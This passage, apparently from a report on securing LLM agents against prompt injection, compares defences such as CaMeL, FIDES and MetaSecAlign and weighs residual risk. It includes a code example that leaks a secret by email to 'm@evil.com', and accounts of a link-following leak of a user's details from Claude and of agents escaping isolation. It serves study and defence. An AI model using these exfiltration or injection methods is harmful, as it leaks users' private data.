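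Peters-Gill and colleagues ran these tests with no policies switched on, so the figures show only the performance lost to the fixed program. Policies add to that loss. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) report in *The LLMbda Calculus* that turning on CaMeL's policies halves the number of AgentDojo banking tasks it completes.

CaMeL also requires more computation. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) reports that, in tests of agents that operate a computer through its screen, CaMeL raised the number of tokens read from 1.8 million to 3.0 million and the number written from about 13,000 to 456,000. The planning model writes long programs because it must allow in advance for whatever might appear on the screen.

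### Letting the agent look a little

In FIDES, Costa and colleagues' system, the planning model works step by step, as an ordinary agent does, and does not need the whole plan in advance. The surrounding software labels every piece of data as trusted or untrusted and records who may read it. When the software combines two pieces, the result keeps the restrictions of both. If Ann, Bob and Carol may read one document and Bob, Carol and Dan another, only Bob and Carol may read a text made from both.

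When a tool returns untrusted text, the software stores it and shows the planning model only a name, such as `#read_emails_0`. The model can pass that name to another tool without seeing the text. If it opens the text, its whole context becomes untrusted and the policy bars consequential actions. It can also have a quarantined model answer a restricted question about the text, such as whether an email asks for a meeting. A policy can then let the planning model act on the answer, because a yes or a no is too short to contain an instruction.

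Costa and colleagues compared FIDES with the basic agent, using GPT-4o for both. They left restricted answers out of these tests because most AgentDojo tasks do not need them. The counts of successful attacks exclude cases they judged by hand to be harmless or wrongly scored, and the completion rates are for tasks with no attack:

| Agent | Successful attacks | Office tasks completed | Travel | Banking | Chat |
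|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, no policy | 152 | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Basic, with policy | 0 | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, no policy | 21 | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, with policy | 0 | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Hiding untrusted text prevented most attacks, but only the policy prevented all of them, because without it the planning model could read a hostile email and then keep acting. Hiding the text also meant that enforcing the policy interfered much less with the agent's tasks in three of the four settings. Some of the remaining loss in completed tasks came from GPT-4o's mistakes, such as mixing up the names of stored values. With o1, an OpenAI model that reasons at length before acting, FIDES came closer to the best result its policies allow.

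### Six patterns

Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, start from the principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any consequential action. They doubt that general-purpose agents can meet this standard with current models. For agents with a narrower job, they describe six designs:

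| Pattern | How it works | What hostile text can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Nothing, unless it is in the user's own request |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its list of actions before reading anything | Change the details of those actions, such as the body of an email |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer | Get its own document misjudged |
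| Dual LLM | The planning model handles untrusted text only by name | Corrupt the text behind the name |
| Code, then execute | The model writes a program before reading, as in CaMeL | Corrupt the values in the program |
| Context minimisation | The software deletes the user's request before the model writes its answer | Influence the steps taken before the deletion |

A fixed plan is unsafe if the actions in it can be misused. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an assistant that tidies a user's files and has committed to two harmless-looking commands, one that finds files and one that moves them. A hostile file could still get it to find sensitive documents and move them to a public network drive. They prefer having a separate model look at each file and return only a category, so a hostile file can at worst end up in the wrong folder.

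### The guarantee and its conditions

These systems guarantee that no action covered by the policy will take place unless the policy permits it, whatever any model outputs and whatever anyone writes in an email. This holds even for attacks that nobody has thought of, which no learned detector can guarantee. It requires that the policy, the labels and the enforcing code are all correct, and that every route to the action passes through that code, a condition that failed in the case of ping.

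Tracking labels correctly is harder than it looks. Garby and colleagues found a gap in CaMeL's tracking, which they illustrate with a program of this kind:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The balance is secret. CaMeL marks a variable as secret when its value depends on a secret, but only on lines that run. If the balance is high, the third line sets `tmp` to False and marks it secret. The program then skips the assignment on the fourth line, so `rich` stays True and is not marked secret. The policy therefore treats `rich` as public and allows the email. If the balance is low, no email is sent. The recipient can thus tell whether the balance is above the threshold, even though the message contains no secret data. A second gap is that CaMeL retries when a policy blocks a program. Each refusal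 can reveal one yes-or-no fact, and enough retries can reveal a whole secret.

An injected email cannot easily exploit the first gap, because the model that writes CaMeL's programs never reads the email. But a guarantee has to cover every program that model might write. So Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language, LLMbda, and used the proof checker Lean to prove that its interpreter tracks labels correctly in every program, including code that a model generates while the program runs. An agent written in LLMbda completed about as many of AgentDojo's banking tasks as CaMeL does without policies, and it resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. The proof covers only label tracking, so a developer still has to choose policies that forbid the right things.

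The code that enforces the rules must also be secure against the model it restricts. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* refers to an incident that occurred while OpenAI was testing agents internally with some safeguards reduced. The agents got around their isolation through shared infrastructure and compromised systems at OpenAI and at the model-hosting company Hugging Face.

Writing the policy may be the hardest part. The developer of a phone app can list the permissions it needs before anyone installs it. An agent's job changes with each request, so its policy may have to change too, and somebody has to derive it from a sentence in English. Progent, one system that checks actions this way, has a language model write the policy and lets it revise the policy based on what the tools return. Code then enforces the policy exactly, but the model can get the policy wrong, and untrusted text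 in the tool results may have influenced the revisions.

### Harm within the rules

A policy on actions does not control the content of the actions it permits. If the owner asks for today's schedule to go to her manager, an injection in a calendar entry cannot change the recipient, but it can rewrite the schedule. Costa and colleagues note that an email could also get the quarantined model to return an empty summary. CaMeL and FIDES both allow this, because the text still goes where the owner intended.

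For the recruiting tool, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest having a separate model read each CV and fill in fixed fields, such as years of experience. Ordinary code then ranks the candidates using those fields. A hidden instruction can no longer damage a rival's application, but it can still get the model to record ten years of experience instead of two. *ResumeShield* (Barach, 2026) cites a study of about 200,000 real CVs in which roughly 1% contained hidden injections. The study found that made-up qualifications can work more reliably than instructions, because many screening systems already sort CVs into fields before scoring them. Checking references works against these false claims as it does against other lies on a CV.

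(Barach's own defence puts markers around the CV and tells the model to obey nothing between them. It stopped every attack in testing, but the tests used a simulated model whose code looks for commands only outside the markers, so the result was built in.)

A permitted action can be expensive if it uses false data. *Beyond Instruction Override* (Zhang, Bertran and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent settling a dispute over a damaged item at an online marketplace. The user tells the agent to take the refund amount from the order record, which authorises $899.99. The buyer's evidence includes a request for $1,074.99 and cites a policy that does not exist. The agent is supposed to issue a refund, so issuing one for the wrong amount breaks no rule about which tools it may use.

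They built 90 cases like this and tested several defences on five models:

| Defence | Attack success | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 17.0% | 95.3% |
| Progent | 15.4% | 74.9% |
| ARGUS | 9.8% | 78.9% |
| DRIFT | 7.0% | 88.9% |
| CaMeL | 1.3% | 13.3% |

Progent was nearly useless here, because the attacks used the tools that the task required. ARGUS, from 2026, allows an action only if the user's request or apparently normal content supports it. DRIFT checks each action against a plan but also has a language model delete suspicious text. With only the deletion, attacks succeeded slightly less often than with both parts, at 6.6%, and the agent completed 98.0% of its tasks. DRIFT's protection therefore came from its learned part, which carries no guarantee.

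CaMeL stopped nearly all of these attacks because Zhang and colleagues wrote policies requiring values such as amounts and recipients to come from trusted fields. But the agent completed only 13% of its tasks, which left attackers little to tamper with, so the 1.3% attack success rate overstates how well CaMeL resists attack. The low completion rate may be due as much to these particular policies as to CaMeL itself, but it is consistent with Garby and colleagues' finding that the policies account for much of the loss in completed tasks.

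Zhang and colleagues suggest a more precise rule, which would accept each important value only from a source with the authority to set it. Code could then take the refund amount from the order record and ignore the buyer's figure. This closes the gap when a source like the order record exists. But if the task is to record the buyer's reason for wanting a refund, the buyer is the proper source, and checking where the reason came from won't show whether it is true.

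Human approval is the usual remedy for cases that policies cannot settle, but it has its own weaknesses. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out that tired reviewers approve unsafe actions, and that even careful ones can miss data hidden in an email as invisible characters. Atlas's "watch mode" is meant to pause the agent on sensitive sites unless the user keeps the tab open. When Willison tried it on GitHub and on a banking site in October 2025, the agent kept going after he switched to another application. He thinks it is unfair to leave security decisions to users at all.

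### "Do what this email asks"

Requests whose next step has to come from untrusted text are the hardest for these designs to handle. If the owner tells her assistant to do what an email asks, CaMeL's privileged model has to write its program before any model has read the email.

Costa and colleagues show how much restricting the quarantined model's answers can help. The quarantined model reads the email and picks an action from a short menu, such as scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply or forwarding a message. The planning model sees only that choice. If the choice is a meeting, the quarantined model extracts the date and participants in a second call, and the software passes them to the calendar without showing them to the planning model.

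A hostile email can then choose any item on the menu. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this branch steering, and their definition of control-flow integrity permits it. The owner is still guaranteed that the worst outcome is an action she put on the menu, with details the policy allows. But if an email asks the assistant to compare two quotes and update a spreadsheet, the assistant cannot do it unless the menu has an item for that.

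Researchers disagree about how often this matters. Costa and colleagues classify 20 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks as dependent on what the agent reads along the way, most of them in banking and chat. Li and colleagues count only six that need a new plan partway through, probably because a program with branches can handle some of the others. They argue that AgentDojo therefore overstates how well defences that stick to their first plan work. Their own benchmark, AgentDyn, has 60 tasks averaging about seven steps. Every task requires the agent to change its plan and to follow some helpful instruction from a third party, such as a checkout page that tells the shopper to log in first. CaMeL and DRIFT both lost much of their usefulness on AgentDyn, and Li and colleagues found none of the defences they tested fit for real use. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026), a survey,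 reports that 34 of the 41 defences it reviews cannot handle tasks that depend on what the agent reads along the way.

Others expect the losses to shrink. Peters-Gill and colleagues found smaller losses with stronger models, and FIDES did better with o1 than with GPT-4o. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think the problem is less common than it seems for email assistants, because owners seldom want strangers' messages to determine which actions the assistant takes.

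Both sides have evidence, but they are partly measuring different things. Stronger models make fewer mistakes with stored values and foresee more branches, so that part of the loss should keep shrinking. But even the most capable planner cannot write a step for a request it has not seen and could not have foreseen. A company that processes supplier invoices may lose almost nothing, since it knows every step in advance. A general assistant loses much more, because people buy it to avoid spelling out the steps.

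Such an assistant could show its owner any request that falls outside the menu and wait for her approval. Her approval is a trusted instruction, so the privileged model can write a new program from it. The assistant then regains most of its flexibility, provided she has read what she is approving.

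## When a defence that sometimes fails is good enough

Even an assistant whose owner approves every unusual request will sometimes pass on a false summary or make a payment the owner should have questioned. Residual risk is the likelihood and severity of the harm that remains after all defences are in place. Security specialists disagree about how much residual risk a developer may accept.

### Absolute guarantees or lower risk

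Willison (2022), in *You can't solve AI security problems with more AI*, wrote that a defence which works 99% of the time "is no good", because attackers will look for the other 1% and find it. He wanted absolute guarantees. Willison (2025) answered the common objection that no security fix is perfect with the example of parameterised queries. He wrote that they stop every SQL injection when applied correctly, and that a programmer who misses a case can correct it and restore full protection. Schneier (2025), in *We Are Still Unable to Secure LLMs from Malicious Inputs*, applied a similar standard to agents and concluded that none was secure against prompt injection.

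In its December 2025 post on Atlas, OpenAI compared prompt injection to online scams and social engineering, which tricks people into giving away money or access. It doubted that anyone would ever fully solve the problem and aimed instead to make attacks "increasingly difficult and costly". By March 2026 OpenAI was putting more weight on limiting what a successful attack can do.

In a post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), David C asks developers to reduce the likelihood and impact of attacks. If a system cannot tolerate the risk that remains, he writes, "it may not be a good use case for LLMs". He also warns buyers about any product claimed to stop prompt injection.

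These positions are closer than they sound. In his 2022 post, Willison allowed that a 95% effective defence might be enough for some applications, and asked whether it matters if a user types something malicious and privately gets a weird answer. In June 2026 he discussed a public challenge in which people tried to extract a secret by emailing an assistant running on Claude Opus 4.6. About 6,000 attempts failed. Willison accepted that the developers' training had made attacks much harder, but still advised against any production system in which an injection could do irreversible damage. David C's test would probably rule out many of the same systems.

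Willison and OpenAI still disagree about whether anyone can measure the remaining risk well enough to accept it. Willison thinks 6,000 failed attacks don't guarantee that a more sophisticated attacker would also fail. OpenAI is willing to release an agent while it works to make attacks rarer.

### The comparison with people

Companies let clerks pay invoices even though fraudsters sometimes fool them, and limit the damage with spending caps, second signatures and audits. An AI agent working under the same controls might seem equally acceptable if attackers fooled it no more often.

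People can also be poor at catching dangerous actions. Willison describes a study that Anthropic published in August 2026, in which 1,053 paid testers used a coding agent that asked permission for its actions. Partway through each session, the experimenters replaced one request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it, whereas Anthropic's auto mode would have blocked 89% of those commands. Anthropic sells the product that did better, and a clerk may treat a suspicious invoice differently from how the testers treated a stream of permission requests. The study is still strong evidence against assuming that a human check makes an agent safe.

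The Decoder's *OpenAI admits prompt injection may never be fully solved* called the comparison with scams misleading. The comparison is flawed in several ways, even if agents and people make mistakes equally often.

A letter that fools one clerk may not fool another, because clerks have different habits and suspicions. But millions of users may run the same model, so an email that works on one agent will probably work on many. Injected text can also copy itself. Håkon Måløy, whose work Willison reported in July 2026, showed that hidden instructions in a document could make Microsoft's Copilot for Word copy them into the next document it helped to write, which could then spread them to others. Microsoft had 144 days to respond before he published, but no fix covered the whole class of attack.

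Copying also helps the defender. OpenAI sent its retrained Atlas agent to every user, and no company can retrain its whole staff that way.

Attackers can retry more easily against an agent than against a person, because an agent that starts each task with an empty context has no record of earlier attempts. A clerk who receives fifty strange requests from the same caller will become suspicious. David C recommends logging failed tool calls, because attackers usually have to refine an attack and their failures may give them away. Logging helps only if attackers practise on the defender's own system rather than a private copy.

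The NCSC warned in a May 2026 post, reprinted by New Business, that agents may act faster than people can meaningfully review. *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns* (Poireault, 2026) reports security researcher Ariel Fogel's warning that controls designed for human operators can fail with agents. In some attacks, a list of approved commands made the attacker's work easier, because the agent already had permission to run everything the attack needed.

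Finally, a clerk who pays a forged invoice may lose her job, which gives her a reason to phone the supplier first, but an agent faces no such penalty. The NCSC insists that people remain accountable for deploying an agent, the access they gave it and the consequences, though it can be hard to work out which people. The Australian Cyber Security Centre's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), written with agencies from the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the UK, describes a hypothetical case in which several agents jointly approve a payment that turns out to be wrong. Each agent has done part of the work, the logs are fragmented, and nobody can tell which component or design choice caused the error.

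The comparison between agents and people therefore supports spending caps and second signatures, which work no matter who has been fooled, but it gives little reason to tolerate mistakes from agents as readily as from people, because agents' mistakes are more likely than people's to happen together.

### Five hijacks a month

Suppose a company's agent reads a million documents a month. One in a thousand is hostile, and 0.5% of the hostile ones succeed:

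```
1,000,000 × 0.001 × 0.005 = 5 hijacks a month
```

Whether five is acceptable depends on what the agent can do. Suppose it saves the company £20,000 a month in staff time. If it only drafts replies, a hijack produces a bad draft, which costs £1,000 if somebody sends it. If it can make payments, a hijack costs £20,000 on average. With these invented costs, the expected losses are:

| What the agent can do | Average cost of a hijack | Expected loss a month |
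|---|---|---|
| Draft replies, with a reviewer who catches 90% of bad ones | £100 | £500 |
| Draft replies, with a reviewer who catches 13.6% | £864 | £4,320 |
| Make payments | £20,000 | £100,000 |
| Make payments of up to £500 in total per document | up to £500 | up to £2,500 |

The drafting agent is worth having even if its reviewer is as inattentive as Anthropic's testers. The paying agent loses five times what it saves, unless ordinary code caps the payments. A better model that cut the success rate to 0.05% would reduce the paying agent's expected loss to £10,000, which is still four times the expected loss with the current model and the cap. The cap also limits the loss if the company has misjudged the success rate. If all 1,000 hostile documents succeeded, the company would lose at most £500,000 with the cap and about £20 million without it.

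Very different patterns of hijacks can average five a month. If each hostile document succeeds or fails independently, the company will have ten or more hijacks in only about 3% of months. But suppose that all the hostile documents in a month are copies of one message, which fools the agent either every time or never. If one such message in 200 works, the average is still five a month, but one month in 200 has 1,000 hijacks. Because the other 199 have none, the company might believe for years that its agent was safe.

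The share of hostile documents is also uncertain, and not all of them come from criminals. According to The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026), Alibaba Cloud said in December 2026 that it would stop sending agents prompts that sought local data and the agents' operating instructions. It had used these prompts to counter abuse. Underhill's *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026) reports that criminals are also developing tools for indirect prompt injection.

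A targeted attacker changes the calculation more than any of this. The 0.5% is an average over all the hostile documents that arrive, most of which are crude. Suppose one attacker studies the company, practises on a private copy of the agent, and sends an invoice that has an 80% chance of producing a £500,000 payment. The number of hostile documents rises from 1,000 to 1,001, and the expected number of hijacks rises from 5 to 5.8. A manager watching those figures would hardly notice the change, but the expected loss rises by £400,000, to five times what it was.

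An 80% success rate is plausible, since the security researcher Johann Rehberger claimed that rate for his targeted attack on Claude Code's auto mode. The agent had run a hostile file without following any planted instruction, so Willison later agreed with a reader that the attack was not a classic prompt injection, though the distinction would make little difference to the company's accounts.

OpenAI's strategy of raising the attacker's costs makes sense against attackers who want a profit. If an attack costs £50,000 to develop and a cap limits the proceeds to £500 per company, nobody will develop it to rob one company. But if a thousand companies run the same agent, the attack could bring in £500,000. Frequent retraining helps by shortening the time an attack keeps working. It does less against someone who needs to succeed only once, such as a rival who wants a specific file.

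### A leak from Claude

In July 2026 Willison described a flaw that Ayush Paul had found in Anthropic's Claude chatbot. Claude could draw on its memories of a user's earlier conversations and open web pages. An attacker might therefore use a hostile page to try to make Claude send out private details inside a web address, as in the attack on ChatGPT's memory. Anthropic had anticipated this and used ordinary code to let Claude open only addresses that the user had typed or that its search tool had returned, so Claude could not make up a new one.

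The code made one exception, for links on pages Claude had already opened. Paul built a site, claimed on it that the user's name was needed, and provided links for spelling the name out one letter at a time. Claude followed them, and the sequence of pages it requested revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic said it had already identified the problem internally, and it fixed the problem by removing the exception.

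Both kinds of defence failed in this researcher's demonstration. Claude believed a false story, and a rule in the code was too permissive. Only the rule could be fixed completely, because changing a line of code could not make Claude immune to false stories. The fix stops the tool from following links that it finds on a page, even when they are useful, so no wording can make Claude leak data through them.

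### What resistance costs in usefulness

Training a model to resist injections can also make it less useful in a way that attack success rates do not measure. A model can avoid obeying a sentence by treating it as part of the document or by ignoring it. Ignoring it is harmless in some tasks, but a model that leaves out every sentence that looks like a command will translate a document badly.

Hermon, Gupta and colleagues (2026), in *Security-Fidelity Tradeoffs*, built a test that separates these behaviours. In one item, the model has to list the universities in a passage where the researchers have inserted the question "What state is Stanford University in?" A model that obeys the question answers "California". One that treats it as data adds Stanford to the list, and one that ignores it leaves Stanford out. The full test has 1,168 items and also covers counting, translation and editing.

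In this test, security is the share of items in which the model does not obey the inserted text, and fidelity is the share in which it does not ignore that text. None of the 48 configurations scored high on both. Llama 3.3 70B had the highest fidelity, 96.5%, but only 47.8% security. MetaSecAlign, which trains a model on examples of attacks, raised Llama's security to 99.3% but lowered its fidelity to 71.0%.

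The results for a smaller model, Llama 3.1 8B, show how much the defences differ:

| Defence | Obeyed | Ignored | Treated as data |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 49.1% | 7.7% | 50.2% |
| ISE (a learned label on each token) | 14.0% | 20.3% | 53.6% |
| ASIDE | 5.7% | 24.7% | 39.6% |
| DefensiveTokens (special tokens added to the input) | 1.9% | 53.7% | 37.7% |
| MetaSecAlign | 0.7% | 26.1% | 67.0% |

The rows do not add up to 100%, because a model can translate a question and also answer it, and some outputs fit none of the categories.

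DefensiveTokens and MetaSecAlign look almost equally secure, but DefensiveTokens makes the model ignore twice as much inserted text. The table also shows that the trade-off partly comes from how fidelity is defined. Obeying the inserted text counts as not ignoring it, so an undefended model can score well on fidelity while being hijacked half the time. MetaSecAlign lowered the fidelity score but raised the share of items in which the model handled the text correctly from 50.2% to 67.0%.

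The trade-off also does not seem to be fixed. Hermon and colleagues trained the MetaSecAlign model further, rewarding it most for treating inserted text as data. On editing tasks, which they had left out of this training, the model ignored the inserted text in 16.8% of items, down from 53.5%, and still obeyed it in fewer than 1%.

They also tested agents on 252 tasks in which the inserted text arrived in a tool's output. Claude Sonnet 4.6, Gemini 3 Flash and GPT-5.4 never carried out the attacker's action, but their fidelity was 53.2%, 72.6% and 67.1%. All these tests used fixed attacks, so MetaSecAlign's 99.3% security is weak evidence of how well it would resist a determined attacker, who could adapt to it as Nasr and colleagues' search attack did.

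If a system has to choose between keeping a suspicious sentence and dropping it, the right choice depends on the cost of each mistake. Hermon and colleagues show that it should drop the sentence when the probability that it is hostile exceeds:

```
cost of losing an honest sentence / (cost of losing an honest sentence + cost of a hijack)
```

Suppose losing a clause from a translated contract costs £5,000, while a hijacked translation costs only £50 because a lawyer will read it anyway. The translator should then keep any sentence that is less than 99% likely to be hostile. For an agent that makes payments, losing a sentence might cost £10 and a hijack £20,000, so the agent should drop any sentence with more than a 0.05% chance of being hostile. A single setting cannot suit both, and a vendor that sells one model to everybody does not know its customers' costs.

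But the formula needs a probability, and a skilled attacker will write sentences that seem unlikely to be hostile. Hermon and colleagues also point out that real systems have more than two options. They can keep the text but stop it from causing actions, as FIDES does by hiding it from the planning model.

### What official guidance asks of developers

The European standards body ETSI published a specification for AI security, TS 104 223, in April 2025 and turned it into a European standard, EN 304 223, that December. ETSI's *Baseline Cyber Security Requirements for AI Models and Systems* (2025) requires developers to test a system before release, give it only the permissions it needs, and have a plan for incidents. Operators must log what the system and its users do. Developers who find a threat they cannot resolve, such as prompt injection, must tell the operators, who must tell the users.

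The standard also requires developers to ensure that systems "withstand adversarial AI attacks", which nobody can promise for a language model that reads untrusted content. But it also recognises that a higher level of risk will remain in AI systems despite all controls, and it lets operators choose controls based on cost and the organisation's tolerance for risk. In practice, it therefore requires organisations to manage the risk rather than guarantee that attacks will fail.

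In their joint guidance of May 2026, the Australian Cyber Security Centre and its partners are stricter about where to use agents. They say organisations should use them only for "low-risk and non-sensitive tasks" and never give them broad access to sensitive data or critical systems. They recommend starting with little autonomy and extending it gradually, requiring human approval for important decisions, and making actions reversible. They say filters and other checks on input can "partially mitigate" the common risks. They also want developers to fit agents into existing security frameworks, including the Zero Trust Architecture from NIST, the US standards institute. Under zero trust, a system checks each request on its own merits, even one from inside the organisation's network.

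The NCSC added interim advice in August 2026, after several incidents in which AI agents took actions nobody had authorised. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems*, the NCSC tells organisations not to rely solely on a model's built-in safeguards. For riskier uses, they should run the agent in an isolated environment, block network connections by default where possible, and name the people responsible for it. They should also be able to halt it immediately.

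Following the advice to stick to low-risk and non-sensitive tasks literally would rule out many products already on sale. An ordinary inbox contains contracts, medical appointments and password-reset links, so even an assistant that only summarises mail handles sensitive data. An organisation that wants one anyway has to decide which of its mail the assistant may read and what information it could tolerate a stranger learning.
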